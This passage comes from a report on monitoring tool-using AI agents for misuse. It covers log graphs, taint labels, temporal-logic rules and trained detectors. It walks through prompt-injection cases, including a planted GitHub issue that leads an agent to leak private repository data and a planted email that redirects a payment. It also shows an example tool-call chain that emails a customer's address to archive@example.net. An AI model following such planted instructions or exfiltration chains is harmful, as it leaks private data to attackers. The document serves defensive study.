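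Clear limits can also prevent some of this behaviour. Qu, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Overeager Coding Agents*, gave agents harmless tasks with opportunities to overstep, such as cleaning up a folder that also held the only copy of some passwords. Claude Code never overstepped when the prompt stated what the user had authorised, but it did in 17.1% of runs when the researchers removed only that passage. Users rarely write such a passage, so the operator has good reason to supply one.

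### Stating the expected outputs for each task

An operator can write down the outputs that each type of task should produce. The shop's list might look like this:

| Task | Outputs allowed | Recipient | Content |
|---|---|---|---|
| Order status | one email | the address on the order | one order, no attachment |
| Overdue orders | one email | the manager who asked | order numbers and dates only |
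| Weekly sales figures | one report, one file, one email | the manager who asked | totals by product, no customer details |

The order-status row does not include a report, a file or a second email, so all three extra calls in the example would raise an alert. The agent can still use the same report tool for the weekly sales figures.

The list has to be closed, meaning any output not on it counts as unexpected. Banerjee and colleagues' tests show why. Each task comes with a contract that can specify required calls, their arguments and order, the reply, the final records and anything forbidden. A run must meet every condition in the contract to pass, but nothing else is checked. A contract that only listed the two lookups and the email to Reyes as required calls would pass the session that leaked the customer list.

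Banerjee and colleagues' results also suggest keeping misuse alerts separate from quality checks. On the tasks that included prohibitions, 876 of 2,640 runs failed, but 644 of those failures broke no prohibition. If every failed run raised an alert, about three-quarters of the alerts would concern incomplete or incorrect work. Banerjee and colleagues count a forbidden call even when the tool refuses it. Security teams should do the same, because a blocked export is still a sign that something is wrong.

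Operators can also label the tools themselves. *Small agents should know what their tools do* (2026) proposes declaring whether each tool only calculates, reads data, makes a correctable change or does something irreversible. Software can then replay a trace and check that the user confirmed every irreversible call, without using a language model. When applied to one untrained model, this check found 94 unconfirmed deletions and sent messages. Labels take little effort to add, but they don't distinguish between uses of the same tool. In the shop, the email to Reyes and the email with the customer list use the same irreversible tool, so the check would treat them alike unless the shop counted the original question as confirmation of the reply. Operators who require approval before an export must also decide whether the original request counts as approval.

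A list of expected outputs works best when the tasks are predictable. The contact form could ask customers to choose "order status" from a menu, and the detector could then apply the matching row. A general assistant for staff gets requests that nobody listed in advance, so a person or another model would have to work out the expected outputs from each request.

Data can also leave inside an output that the list allows. If Reyes persuaded the agent to include another customer's home address in the reply, the log would show one email to the right person with no attachment. To catch this, the shop would need to check the email's content too. One of Banerjee and colleagues' checks similarly forbids any call whose arguments contain another person's identifiers.

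## Chained outputs: when one call's result feeds the next

To determine whether an email contains data it shouldn't, a detector must trace the content to its source, which is often an earlier call. Tool calls have chained outputs when the result of one becomes the input of the next, as when the shop's agent copies a shipping date from an order lookup into its reply. Agents do this constantly, but a chain can do harm even when the agent has permission for every call in it.

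Suppose someone persuades the shop's agent to pass on another customer's home address.

| Call | Tool | Arguments | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | search_customers | Okafor | G. Okafor, 14 Mill Lane, Leeds |
| 2 | write_file | note.txt: "G. Okafor, 14 Mill Lane, Leeds" | note.txt saved |
| 3 | send_email | to archive@example.net, with note.txt | sent |

The agent is allowed to search customers, write files and email people outside the shop, so a check that examines each call separately passes all three. Flagging call 3 would require the result of call 1. *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* (2026) describes a similar case in an office, where an agent retrieves a confidential document, summarises it, drafts a message and sends it outside. The proposed remedy is to remove the agent's permission to send anything outside for the rest of the session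 once it has read something confidential. That would stop the theft of Okafor's address, but if the shop treats its order records as confidential, it would also stop the agent from telling Reyes that order 4417 has shipped.

A chain can also run through several services. *Signed, Sealed, Leaked* (2026) includes an attack in which data from one tool server ends up in authorised requests to a second server, which sends it out. Each server's log would show only half of the attack. *MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to tool-using agents, lists other variants, such as writing sensitive data to a log that the attacker reads later, or combining many harmless details into sensitive information.

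### Private data, untrusted text and a way out

Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, describes agents that combine three things: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate with the outside. He argues that an attacker can easily trick any such agent into fetching private data and sending it out.

The shop's agent has all three: private data in its customer records, untrusted text in the contact form and delivery notes, and a way to send data out by email. Willison advises avoiding the combination, but the shop can't do that without giving up the service. Some tools supply more than one of the three. A mailbox, for example, holds private data, and anyone can put untrusted text in it by sending a message.

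Stolen data can leave without a tool that has "send" in its name, which makes the leak easy to overlook in a log. Willison points out that loading an image from the web can carry data out, as can a link that the user clicks. *Flowsh* (Kim, Trampert and colleagues, 2026) treats every web request as a possible leak, even one that only reads a page, because the requested address can contain the stolen data and the server can keep it.

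An agent can have all three ingredients for years without incident, so their presence is better evidence of a risky set-up than of misuse in any one session. A log detector can look for sessions that use all three, where the agent takes in untrusted text, reads private data and then sends something out. But it shouldn't require the untrusted text, because the agent in the earlier example sent every customer's address to a courier with only private data and a way to send it.

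### The GitHub connector leak of May 2025

GitHub stores software projects' code in public or private repositories, and its official connector lets an agent read and change them. Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) describes a demonstration in which a harmless request led an agent to publish private data through this connector. The demonstration user had a public repository for a Pacman game and several private ones. Anyone can file an issue (a bug report or comment) on a public repository, and the researchers filed one with planted instructions. In the text, which Willison quotes in *GitHub MCP Exploited*, they complained that the project's author was not widely recognised and asked for someone to read the README file (the introductory page) of all the author's repositories and add a chapter.

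The user then asked Claude 4 Opus to look at the open issues. In outline, the log would read as follows.

| Entry | Call | Result or effect |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | Read the issues in the public Pacman repository | Issues, including the planted text |
| 2 | Read files in the private repositories | Names of private projects, the user's plan to move to South America, the user's salary |
| 3 | Open a pull request (a proposed change) in the Pacman repository, containing these details | Anyone can read it |

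One connector supplied all three ingredients, and every call went to GitHub, so a detector that looked for unfamiliar destinations would have found nothing. Detecting the leak requires knowing that the repositories in entry 2 were private and the one in entry 3 was public, which means looking up their settings if the log doesn't record them.

The two steps of the chain also leave different evidence. Private details from entry 2 reappear in the pull request in entry 3, so comparing the text would connect the two entries. There is much less to compare between entries 1 and 2, because the planted request was for "all" the repositories without naming any, so it would be easier to tell from the log what leaked than why it leaked.

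Claude Desktop, which the researchers used, asks the user to confirm each call by default, but Invariant Labs notes that many users choose "Always Allow" and stop watching. It recommends a rule that raises a violation when an agent uses two repositories in one session. The rule would have stopped this chain at entry 2, but it would also stop a developer's agent from copying a bug fix between projects, because it compares only the repositories' names and owners.

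GitHub (2025) later made a narrower change. Since August 2025, its hosted connector has scanned the inputs of tool calls in public repositories for exposed secrets and, by default, blocked any call that contains one. This should help with leaked access keys, which tend to have a recognisable format, but the scan would presumably have let this pull request through because salaries and plans to emigrate have no such format.

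### Turning a log into a graph

Software can search for chains by turning each session's log into a graph, a set of points (nodes) joined by links. It takes three steps:

1. Make each tool call a node that holds the tool's name, the arguments and the result.
2. Link each call to the one that follows it in time.
3. Compare each result with the arguments of every later call. If part of the result reappears there, add a data-flow link between the two calls.

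The third step needs a rule for what counts as reappearing. Zavrak (2026), in *Content-Aware Attack Detection in LLM Agent Tool-Call Traffic*, adds a data-flow link if either of these conditions holds:

- The first 50 characters of the earlier call's result appear as an unbroken string in the later call's arguments.
- At least one of the first five words of the result is longer than four characters and appears in the later call's arguments. A "word" is anything between two spaces, so attached punctuation counts.

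Zavrak skips any result longer than 1,000 characters, because long results produce too many chance matches.

There are three pairs of calls to check in the theft of Okafor's address. The search result is only 30 characters long, so the first condition compares all of it.

| Pair | Words long enough to match | Found in the later arguments | Data-flow link? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Search → file | "Okafor," and "Lane," | both, along with the whole result | yes |
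| File → email | "note.txt" and "saved" | "note.txt" | yes |
| Search → email | "Okafor," and "Lane," | neither | no |

("Lane" has only four letters, so it qualifies only because of its comma.) The graph correctly traces the theft from the customer search, through the file, to the outside email. A detector can now look for any path from a tool that reads private data to a tool that sends data out.

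But the result depends on small details. If the file tool had returned only "saved", the second link would be missing and the path would break. If the agent had written "Okafor lives at 14 Mill Lane in Leeds", the first link would be missing too, because neither name would have its comma.

Larger thefts can be harder to detect. In the earlier leak of the whole customer list, the agent ran a report, saved it as customers.csv and emailed the file. The report's 2,310 rows are far longer than 1,000 characters, so the rule skips them. The file tool returned "2,310 rows saved", and none of those words appears in the email call's arguments, so the rule finds no data-flow link between the report, the file and the email.

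The rule does find three meaningless links in the same session. The lookup of order 4417 returned "shipped 3 March; customer 2093", and the word "customer" is long enough to match. It appears inside "all customers" in the report's arguments and inside "customers.csv" in the other two calls, so the rule links the order lookup to all three.

In the harmless part of that session, the agent looks up the order, finds Reyes and sends the reply, and every pair of these calls has a data-flow link. The lookup and the customer search share "customer", the lookup and the email share "shipped", and the search and the email share Reyes's address. Counting links would make these three calls look more suspicious than the report, file and email calls that leaked the list.

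An operator could improve on this by ignoring common words, stripping punctuation and matching distinctive values, such as email addresses, wherever they occur in a result. Lengthening the 50-character string is less promising, because Zavrak tried lengths up to 500 and got the same number of links. The condition on single words already covered every match. Zavrak built the graphs to train classifiers, which got most of their accuracy from the text of the calls and little from the links.

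### What text matching misses and what it links by accident

Any rule that looks for copied text fails when the agent rewrites the data. A summary of Okafor's record could say that she lives off the main road in north Leeds, and a translation could change nearly every word. Encoding also hides the text. In Base64, a common way of writing data as letters and digits, "Okafor" becomes "T2thZm9y". *MCP-38* lists Base64 text inside web addresses as one way to get data out.

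*Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and colleagues, 2026) describes two further gaps. Planted text can change which tool the agent calls even when none of that text appears in the call. For example, an email might announce a new policy of forwarding all mail to an "archive", and the agent might then forward ordinary messages that don't mention the policy. The agent can also save data to its memory in one session and use it days later in another, so neither session's log contains the whole chain.

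The NeuroTaint system runs a series of tests on finished logs. It can add a unique code to a tool's result before the agent reads it, and if the code turns up in a later call, the agent must have copied it. NeuroTaint also checks the result and the later call for shared text, compares their meaning, and repeats that comparison on smaller pieces of long documents. If none of these tests finds a connection, it asks a language model whether the agent would still have made the call if the suspect text had been neutral. It saves its records between sessions, so it can trace data through the agent's memory.

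Cai and colleagues tested NeuroTaint on 400 scenarios of their own. In 200 of them, outside content reached or influenced a later call. NeuroTaint found 187 of these and wrongly flagged 16 of the other 200. It found 37 of the 40 cases in which planted text only changed the agent's decision, which comparing text could not have caught. Seven of its 13 misses were among the 42 cases in which the agent had rewritten the content several times.

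Most of the false alarms came from 14 scenarios in which the agent wrote about the same topic as the outside source without drawing on it. NeuroTaint flagged all of them. Comparing meanings catches paraphrases that word matching misses, but it can also link passages that only share a subject. In the shop, thousands of replies say that an order has shipped, so they would all look related.

### Tracking labels instead of text

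Taint tracking, or information-flow control, labels data when it enters the system and passes the label to anything made from that data, so it doesn't need to compare text. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026), a survey of ways to trace what agents do, dates the idea to work by Dorothy Denning in 1976.

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, use labels with two parts. One says whether the data comes from a trusted source. The other lists who may read it. When the agent combines two pieces of data, the result is trusted only if both pieces were, and only people on both lists may read it:

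readers(x combined with y) = readers(x) ∩ readers(y)

Suppose the label on order 4417 lists the shop's staff and Reyes as readers, and the label on Okafor's record lists the staff and Okafor. An email that draws on both has the label {staff, Reyes} ∩ {staff, Okafor} = {staff}, so sending it to Reyes would break the policy. The label would be the same even if the agent had summarised, translated or encoded Okafor's address.

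Costa and colleagues describe two basic policies. The first allows a consequential call, such as sending an email, only if everything that influenced it was trusted. The second allows data to leave only if every recipient is permitted to read it. With suitable policies, their system, FIDES, stopped every attack in AgentDojo, a standard set of prompt-injection tests.

The agent's choices can still leak some information. If the agent emails a supplier only when a private stock figure is low, the supplier learns something about the figure by receiving the email, whatever it says. Costa and colleagues accept this leak because preventing it would essentially mean banning any call with publicly visible effects after the agent has read private data.

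Labels have to stay with the data wherever it goes, including into files. In the shop's theft, for example, the address passes through note.txt. This matters even more when an agent runs a script, because the tool-call log leaves out the script's individual steps. Kim and colleagues' system, Flowsh, monitors which files and websites each command actually opens. It stores labels with the files, so the labels last from one session to the next.

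Flowsh is designed to overcount connections between files and outputs. If a command opens a file, Flowsh counts the whole file as read and everything the command produced as influenced by the file's contents. This is safer than missing a connection, but it also puts restrictive labels on harmless outputs.

Such labels tend to spread. Anything a language model has read can shape its output, and the system usually can't tell which parts did, so it gives the output the labels of all of them. After one private read, nearly everything the agent does can end up labeled private. Security researchers call this label creep. In *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026) simulated it in teams of agents that share a task, without using real models. Dividing the work among more agents and giving only a few of them the sensitive tools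 each slowed the spread. But labels still spread in the best possible arrangement, and the paper concludes that systems also need a safe way to remove them.

Cai and colleagues' tests show that crude labelling can cause many false alarms. They compared NeuroTaint with a version of FIDES that treated a path from an outside source to a sensitive tool as strong evidence that data had flowed along it. In 140 of the harmless scenarios, a source and a sensitive tool both appeared but no data passed between them. The FIDES version flagged 94 of these, and NeuroTaint flagged one. The FIDES version also found only 5 of the 30 cases that crossed sessions or agents, because its labels did not last beyond the session.

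More careful tracking can reduce interruptions when it replaces less precise controls. Kim and colleagues compared Flowsh with a permissive sandbox that asked for approval whenever it couldn't guarantee that an action was safe. On office tasks, Flowsh asked for 5.8 times fewer approvals per completed task, but the agent's completion rate was 7.9 percentage points lower. On Terminal-Bench, a set of command-line tasks, it asked for 22.5 times fewer, and the completion rate was 9.7 points lower. Asking less often also has some security value. Kim and colleagues cite Anthropic's finding that users approve about 93% of Claude Code's permission requests and become less attentive as the requests pile up.

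An operator can't add label-based tracking to an old log, because the system has to attach the labels while the agent is running. Somebody also has to decide beforehand who may read each kind of data. Text matching needs only the arguments and results, so it is still useful for investigating sessions that ran without labels.

### "Summarise this and mail it to the client"

Much office work consists of reading something private, rewriting it and sending it to someone outside the company. For example, the shop's manager might ask the agent to summarise the week's late deliveries and email the summary to the courier.

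| Stage | The manager's request | The theft of Okafor's address |
|---|---|---|
| Read private data | run a report on late deliveries | search for Okafor |
| Write it up | save summary.txt | save note.txt |
| Send it out | email summary.txt to the courier | email note.txt to archive@example.net |

The two chains have the same structure. The manager's request can even involve all three of Willison's ingredients, because delivery notes contain text that outsiders wrote. Zhang and colleagues recommend recording when an agent reuses an output as a later input, but say that such reuse is not inherently malicious. An alert on every chain from private data to an outside address would flag the manager's summary and every order update the shop sends.

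The cases differ in who chose the recipient and what the recipient was entitled to see. The manager named the courier, but nobody with authority named archive@example.net. An operator can write rules to check where a recipient's address came from, but checking whether the recipient should see the content takes more judgement. For example, the courier needs the order numbers and delivery addresses, but probably not the customers' phone numbers or what they bought.

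Costa and colleagues use a similar task, in which a user asks an agent to summarise three emails and send the summary to a colleague. An ordinary agent reads the emails before it sends the summary, so text planted in them could change the recipient. FIDES can keep the main model from seeing the emails. A separate model with no tools writes the summary, and the main model sends it on without reading it. The main model has therefore seen only the user's request when it chooses the recipient.

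In the shop, this would keep a planted delivery note from redirecting the summary to a stranger. The note could still put a false complaint into the summary, which the courier would receive from the shop's own address.

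## The case for written rules

A rule is a condition that a person writes and that raises an alert whenever a log meets it. A check on where a recipient's address came from is a rule, as are the thresholds for enumeration and the shop's list of allowed outputs. Rules need no training data, so an operator can run them from the agent's first day. The same log always produces the same result, and when an auditor asks why a session raised an alert, the operator can point to the condition and the call that met it.

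Rules are also fast to check. *Symbolic Temporal Supervision of LLM Agents Using Contracts* (Xiao, Liu and Nuzzo, 2026) tests ContrAgent, which checks each tool call against a library of rules before the call runs. On SOPBench, a set of customer-service tasks with written procedures, the median check took about a tenth of a millisecond with 38 to 65 rules loaded.

SOPBench includes tasks that the procedure permits and tasks that it forbids. Without a safeguard, the agent completed 91% of the permitted tasks but correctly held back on only 32% of the forbidden ones. With ContrAgent's rules, the figures were 90% and 98%. A second language model that judged each call also reached 98% on the forbidden tasks, but it blocked so much that the agent completed only 24% of the permitted ones. With the procedure in its prompt, the agent completed 64% of the permitted tasks and held back on 94% of the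 forbidden ones, but the score on forbidden tasks fell to 45% when Xiao and colleagues switched to a weaker model. The rules still scored 98% with that model. Xiao and colleagues built their rules from SOPBench's own procedures, so this is a test of enforcing a known policy. It doesn't show how easily an operator could work out which rules to write.

A repeatable answer can still be wrong. *ToolGuardian* (Ravindran and Deochake, 2026) gave the same structured facts about tools and tasks to a set of logical rules, to hand-coded checks with risk scores, and to a language model. All three classified all 20 test scenarios correctly. Performance dropped substantially when the researchers removed the conditions about combinations of calls and about tools behaving differently from their descriptions. The test was small, but it suggests that what the conditions cover matters more than what kind of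 software applies them.

### Four kinds of rule

Rules differ in how much of the log the software has to remember.

| The rule uses | Example for the shop: raise an alert if | The software must remember |
|---|---|---|
| One call | the agent emails a spreadsheet to an outside address | nothing |
| A counter | a session touches more than 20 orders | a running total |
| Earlier events | the agent reads an order before confirming who the customer is | which customers it has confirmed |
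| Earlier events and a clock | the agent exports customer data and the manager's approval is over 24 hours old | each approval and its time |

Rules that check a single log entry are the easiest to write and often the crudest. *From Attack Simulation to SIEM Rule* (2026) generates rules for log-monitoring systems. One raises an alert when an agent's reply contains strings such as "send_email", "delete_user" or "execute_sql", which suggest that someone has got the agent to list its tools. The rule includes a note on its known false alarm, a documentation chatbot that describes its tools on purpose.

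A counter catches harm that builds up across calls. Xiao and colleagues give the example of an agent that may make at most two transfers in a session. The third transfer may look just like the first two, so a check on that call alone would pass it.

A rule that checks earlier events can express policies such as "authenticate before accessing data". *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (Kamath, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) describes a retail test in which a customer asks to return a camera and gives an order number. The agent's safeguard was DynaGuard, a language model that checks outputs against a policy, but the agent still fetched the order and disclosed its details without confirming the customer's identity. The paper's rule allows the order lookup only if an earlier call found the user by email and that user owns the order. The calls may not show who owns the order, so the software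 also has to query the shop's database.

A rule with a time limit can allow a call at one time and forbid the same call later. *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Kekatos, Lekidis and colleagues, 2026) demonstrates this with a short constructed log and a rule that consent for an export lasts 24 hours. In the log, someone gives consent at hour 0. An export at hour 12 passes, and one at hour 48 raises an alert. After fresh consent at hour 50, an export at hour 60 passes.

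Some rules measure the limit in events instead of hours, so filtering the log can change what they allow. For example, if a rule requires approval within the last six events and an engineer filters out routine diagnostic entries, an approval that was too old can count again. Ferrando (2026), in *One Monitor Does Not Fit All*, therefore advises checking that the rule still means the same thing whenever the filter changes.

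### Temporal logic in plain words

Rules about the order of events are easy to misread in English, so researchers often write them in temporal logic. It adds words for time, such as "always", "eventually" and "until", to the "and", "or" and "not" of ordinary logic.

Anand, Chatzi and colleagues (2026), in *MENTOR*, explain these with an agent that books business trips:

- Until: the agent books nothing until it has checked the distance.
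- Always: once a check shows a distance below 500 km, the agent never books a flight for that route.
- Eventually: the agent successfully books the trip.

The third requirement makes the agent finish the job, since an agent that checked the distance and then stopped would satisfy the first two. Each requirement applies to one route at a time, so checking the distance from Toronto to Chicago doesn't allow the agent to book a trip to Montreal.

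Rules that require something to happen "eventually" are awkward to check during a run. *AgentLTL* (Elkoussy and Perez, 2026) gives the example that every search must eventually lead to a citation. The agent could still add the citation at any time before it finishes, so the paper's software checks such rules only at the end of the run. It can check many other rules before each call.

Conditions about the past suit alerts better, because the evidence is already in the log. *LEANGUARD* (Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues, 2026) uses three: "previous" (true at the last relevant event), "once" (true at some earlier point) and "since" (true continuously from some earlier event until now). The shop could use "since" to require that a manager approved an export and has not withdrawn the approval.

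*SoK* (2026), a survey of formal methods for checking information, notes that basic temporal logic cannot express a limit on a rate over a moving window. ContrAgent works around this for simple totals by keeping the count in ordinary code and passing to the logic only whether the count is within the limit.

Few operators will want to write formulas. Li, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *VIGIL*, offer six ready-made forms, which the shop could use like this:

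| Form | Example for the shop |
|---|---|
| Absence | The agent never deletes an order. |
| Precedence | The agent issues a refund only after a manager approves it. |
| Response | After every refund, the agent emails the customer. |
| Bounded response | The agent sends that email within its next three calls. |
| Resolution | However often the agent edits an address, the final version passes the address check. |
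| Until | After reading a delivery note, the agent sends no files until a manager confirms. |

A rule can also require two calls to share a value, so that a manager's approval of one refund doesn't cover another.

Li and colleagues tested VIGIL on 152 recorded runs in which agents used "skills", packages of instructions and tools. In 72 of the runs, the agent broke a rule in the skill's documentation. VIGIL found 69 of these and wrongly flagged 8 of the other 80 runs. Two systems that decide on one pending call at a time did worse: AgentSpec found 34 violations with 12 false alarms, and Progent found 40 with 47 false alarms. A language model that read the whole trace found 48, with 5 false alarms. On two other benchmarks, where a single call was usually enough to reveal the violation, VIGIL barely beat the best alternative. Keeping track of earlier calls seems to help mainly when the harm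 depends on them.

In VIGIL, a language model drafts the rules from the documentation, and conventional software applies them. The model can make mistakes in drafting. One skill restricted bulk changes to a calendar, but the draft left out the word "bulk", so VIGIL flagged an agent for moving a single appointment. People make such mistakes too, and Anand and colleagues cite research showing that even experts find it hard to turn written requirements into formulas.

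### Five general rules, replayed on recorded attacks

VIGIL's rules come from the documentation of each skill. Kekatos and colleagues tested how far an operator could get with five general rules that know nothing about the task. Each requires an earlier approval for one class of risky action:

- destroying something, for example by deleting or cancelling it
- turning off a protection
- committing money
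- sending data out
- changing a setting or operating a device.

In symbols, the first rule is

□ ∀a (destructive(a) → ◆ approved(a))

The square means "always", ∀a means "for every action a", the arrow means "only if" and the diamond means "at some earlier point". So the agent may take a destructive action only if someone has already approved it.

The software sorts tools into classes by the words in their names. A tool with "delete" or "purge" in its name counts as destructive, and one with "confirm" or "approve" counts as an approval. Matching names this way is fragile. The first version also treated "ack", short for "acknowledge", as approval. Because "invite_user_to_slack" contains those letters, inviting someone to a Slack workspace counted as approval for whatever the agent did next. Kekatos and colleagues fixed this before producing the results below.

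They applied the rules to recorded runs from three benchmarks, without running any agent. AgentDojo, the set of prompt-injection tests, supplied attacked and harmless runs by GPT-4o. STAC contains 483 attacks, each a chain of innocent-looking calls that ends in a harmful one. R-Judge contains 571 records of agent runs that people have labelled safe or unsafe.

| Recorded runs | Flagged by at least one of the five rules |
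|---|---|
| STAC attack chains | 347 of 483 (71.8%) |
| AgentDojo, successful attacks | 1,354 of 1,931 (70.1%) |
| AgentDojo, harmless runs | 36 of 123 (29.3%) |
| R-Judge, unsafe records | 71 of 301 (23.6%) |
| R-Judge, safe records | 44 of 270 (16.3%) |

(For STAC, the count covers alerts on the final, harmful call.)

Five rules that nobody had adapted to the tasks detected 70% of attacks. But the AgentDojo runs contain no approvals, so the rules' condition about earlier events could never hold. The rules therefore flagged every risky action, and Kekatos and colleagues acknowledge that a list of keywords would have done the same.

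How well a list of risky actions works depends heavily on the domain. On AgentDojo's banking tasks, the five rules together flagged 97.4% of successful attacks but also 79.2% of harmless runs, because banking agents are meant to make payments. On travel tasks, which seldom involve payments or exports, they flagged only 16.5% of successful attacks and 11.1% of harmless runs. A bank would have to loosen the rules to reduce false alarms, while a travel agency would need to add rules to catch more attacks.

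The timing of the alerts was more encouraging. In 52.4% of the successful AgentDojo attacks, a rule raised an alert before the final harmful call, typically one call earlier. In another 17.7%, the first alert came at that call, which is still early enough if the software can hold the call back. No rule raised an alert in the remaining 29.9%. Some of the early alerts may have been luck, since a rule that flags every payment can flag the user's own payment before the attacker's. On STAC, only 11.8% of the chains triggered an alert before the final call, and 61.5% did so only at that call, partly because STAC's chains are designed to cause harm only in the last step.

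### The same three calls with two different payees

Rules work better when the log includes history they can use. Kekatos and colleagues compare two banking runs in which the agent makes the same three calls.

| Call | Legitimate run | Hijacked run |
|---|---|---|
| read_inbox | an invoice from a supplier | a planted instruction to "pay the March difference" |
| get_transactions | past payments, including some with the supplier's account | the same past payments |
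| send_money | to the supplier's account | to an account number found only in the email |

The general rule on payments flags both runs, and the last call alone can't distinguish them because one unfamiliar account number looks much like another. The runs differ in where the number came from. In the legitimate run, it appeared among the past payments before the agent used it.

Kekatos and colleagues turned this into a rule that raises an alert when

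transfer(p) ∧ ¬ ◆ known_payee(p)

In words, the agent transfers money to payee p, and p was not a known payee at any earlier point. (The symbol ∧ means "and", and ¬ means "not".) A payee becomes known when its account number appears in a sender or recipient field of earlier account data. A mention in the text of an email doesn't count.

The fair comparison is with the general payment rule on its own, on the same banking tasks.

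| Single rule, banking tasks | Successful attacks flagged | Harmless runs flagged |
|---|---|---|
| Any payment without approval | 79.2% | 44.0% |
| Payment to an unknown payee | 70.0% | 24.0% |

The payee rule cut false alarms by nearly half but lowered the detection rate by about nine percentage points. With only 25 harmless runs, that meant five fewer false alarms. But when Kekatos and colleagues pooled 700 harmless banking runs by many different models, the payee rule again reduced false alarms, this time by 75. The rule can't add false alarms, because it flags only payments that the general rule would also flag.

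A similar rule for emails to unknown recipients helped less. On office tasks, it reduced the share of harmless runs flagged from 15.2% to 10.9%, while detection fell from 42.5% to 39.2%.

The shop could use this rule for its own emails. The reply about order 4417 would pass because Reyes's address comes from the customer search. An email to archive@example.net would raise an alert because no lookup returned that address. The rule would also flag a legitimate first payment to a new supplier or a first email to a new courier. It depends on the log holding a record of payees or contacts that an attacker can't add to.

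Xiao and colleagues gave their rules a list of legitimate targets for each task in AgentDojo. The rules blocked a consequential call if its target was not on the list and had come from a tool's output instead of the user. In replayed runs from 22 models, this cut the share of attacks that succeeded from 18.0% to 5.3%, with a false-positive rate of 0.8%. However, they drew up the lists partly from the benchmark's reference solutions. An operator could write similar lists for order-status questions, but would struggle to write them for a general assistant.

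### Harm that lies in the meaning of the text

Suppose a customer asks the shop whether a swollen battery is safe to charge, and the agent emails back that it is. The log shows one reply to the right person, with no attachment and nobody else's data. The order of the calls and the counts are also normal. The harm comes entirely from what the reply says.

Many of R-Judge's unsafe records involve misinformation, unsafe advice or private details in a reply, which is why the five general rules flagged only 23.6% of them. Kekatos and colleagues conclude that rules about the structure of a log need to be paired with a method that can judge meaning.

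Xiao and colleagues got a much better result on the same records. With seven rules, ContrAgent detected 87.0% of the unsafe records, and 97.0% of its alerts were correct. ContrAgent can search for patterns in messages as well as in calls, but it probably did better mainly because Xiao and colleagues derived the rules from R-Judge's own list of risk types. An operator who knows which harms to expect can write good rules for them. The result is weak evidence that rules can detect harms nobody has listed. Xiao and colleagues also report that the harm in the records ContrAgent missed lay in their meaning.

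### Sorting alerts and enforcing a few firm prohibitions

Someone who favours rules can accept all this and reply that general rules were never meant to decide cases alone. Kekatos and colleagues call theirs "a triage filter, not a gate". Rules that cost little to run can pick out the sessions that a person, or a slower and more expensive method, should read first. Even for triage, flagging 29.3% of harmless runs is a lot, and most alerts will be false if misuse is rare.

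Written rules can also block a few actions outright. Sankar and colleagues wrote 45 rules covering 43 tools in τ²-bench, a set of customer-service tasks in retail, airlines and telecoms. Without the rules, agents made at least 33 forbidden calls that went through and changed a record. With the rules, no forbidden call went through. When the software also told agents which rule they had broken, they completed 70.9% of tasks, compared with 72.7% without rules, a difference that was not statistically significant.

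The rules were far stricter on DTap, a benchmark of prompt-injection attacks. They let agents read the customer's own records and public data but not change anything. The success rate of direct attacks, which come from the user, fell from 57.9% to 5.9%. The success rate on harmless tasks also fell, from 53.1% to 12.5%, because many of those tasks involved making a change. In telecoms, the harmless tasks needed no changes, and their success rate stayed the same.

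A firm prohibition therefore has little downside when ordinary work never requires the forbidden action. The shop could safely forbid its agent from deleting orders or emailing the full customer list to anyone outside the shop, but it could not forbid all emails to outside addresses, because the agent answers customers by email.

Blocking also affects how to write the rule. Ferrando considers a rule that the agent never makes an unapproved request. One blocked attempt breaks this rule for the rest of the session, because the agent still made the request. Software that blocks calls whenever the rule is broken would then refuse every later call, including approved requests. To avoid this, the blocking rule should check only whether the current call is allowed, given what has actually been done and approved, and a separate rule should record the failed attempt for whoever reviews the alerts.

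## The case for detectors trained on logs

An operator can write rules only for misuse that somebody has thought of. *TraceAegis* (Liu, Ruan and colleagues, 2025) argues that trying to write a complete set of rules takes a lot of manual work and still leaves gaps, because attacks keep changing. The alternative is to train a detector on past logs to learn what normal use looks like and flag departures from it. If someone gets the imaginary shop's agent to email the customer list to a stranger, the detector can flag the email even if nobody foresaw the attack, because the agent has never attached a file to a customer reply in months of logs.

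In *An Intrusion-Detection Model* (1987), Dorothy Denning hypothesized that break-ins and abuse by insiders would show up in a computer system's audit records as abnormal use. She proposed software that would build a statistical profile of each user's habits, such as when they logged in and which files they read, and report activity that didn't fit.

Detectors for agents' logs come in two kinds. A baseline learns from harmless sessions only and scores a new session by how far it departs from them. A classifier learns from sessions people have labelled harmless or attacked and estimates which group a new session belongs to.

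The baseline comes closer to the original promise of catching what nobody foresaw. Zhang, Yu and colleagues (2026), in *Skynet*, point out that labelled attacks are scarce and leave out any threat missing from the list their makers used. But unusual sessions are often harmless. The first time the shop's manager asks for every overdue order, the session will be unlike any other in the log. The baseline can also learn to treat misuse as normal, as it will if the agent has been sending the courier every customer's address since its first week.

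### TraceAegis: learning a workflow from normal sessions

Liu and colleagues' system, TraceAegis, needs only the inputs, outputs and order of tool calls, which a gateway can record without seeing the agent's prompts. It builds its baseline in three steps:

1. It works out from normal sessions which tools follow which, and which can change places.
2. It cuts each session into short units that respect this order.
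3. A language model summarises similar units into conditions, for example that pain in the knee or arm leads to a referral to orthopaedics.

One of the test agents directs patients to hospital departments. It might refer a patient with ankle pain and psychological distress to orthopaedics and then to psychiatry, or in the reverse order. TraceAegis accepts both orders because it splits the session into one unit for each referral. It flags a referral made before the agent has looked up the symptoms. It also flags a referral to the ear, nose and throat department for foot pain, even if the sequence of tools is familiar. TraceAegis in effect learns a set of rules, so nobody has to write them.

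Liu and colleagues generated 1,300 normal and 300 abnormal traces for this agent, and the same numbers for an agent that handles purchasing requests. Using the language model DeepSeek-V3, TraceAegis detected 96.3% of the abnormal clinic traces, and 96.7% of its alerts were correct. DeepSeek-V3 alone detected 77.7%. Performance depends heavily on the language model, as the reported figures imply a false-positive rate of about 3% with DeepSeek-V3 and 36% with the smaller Gemma-3-27B.

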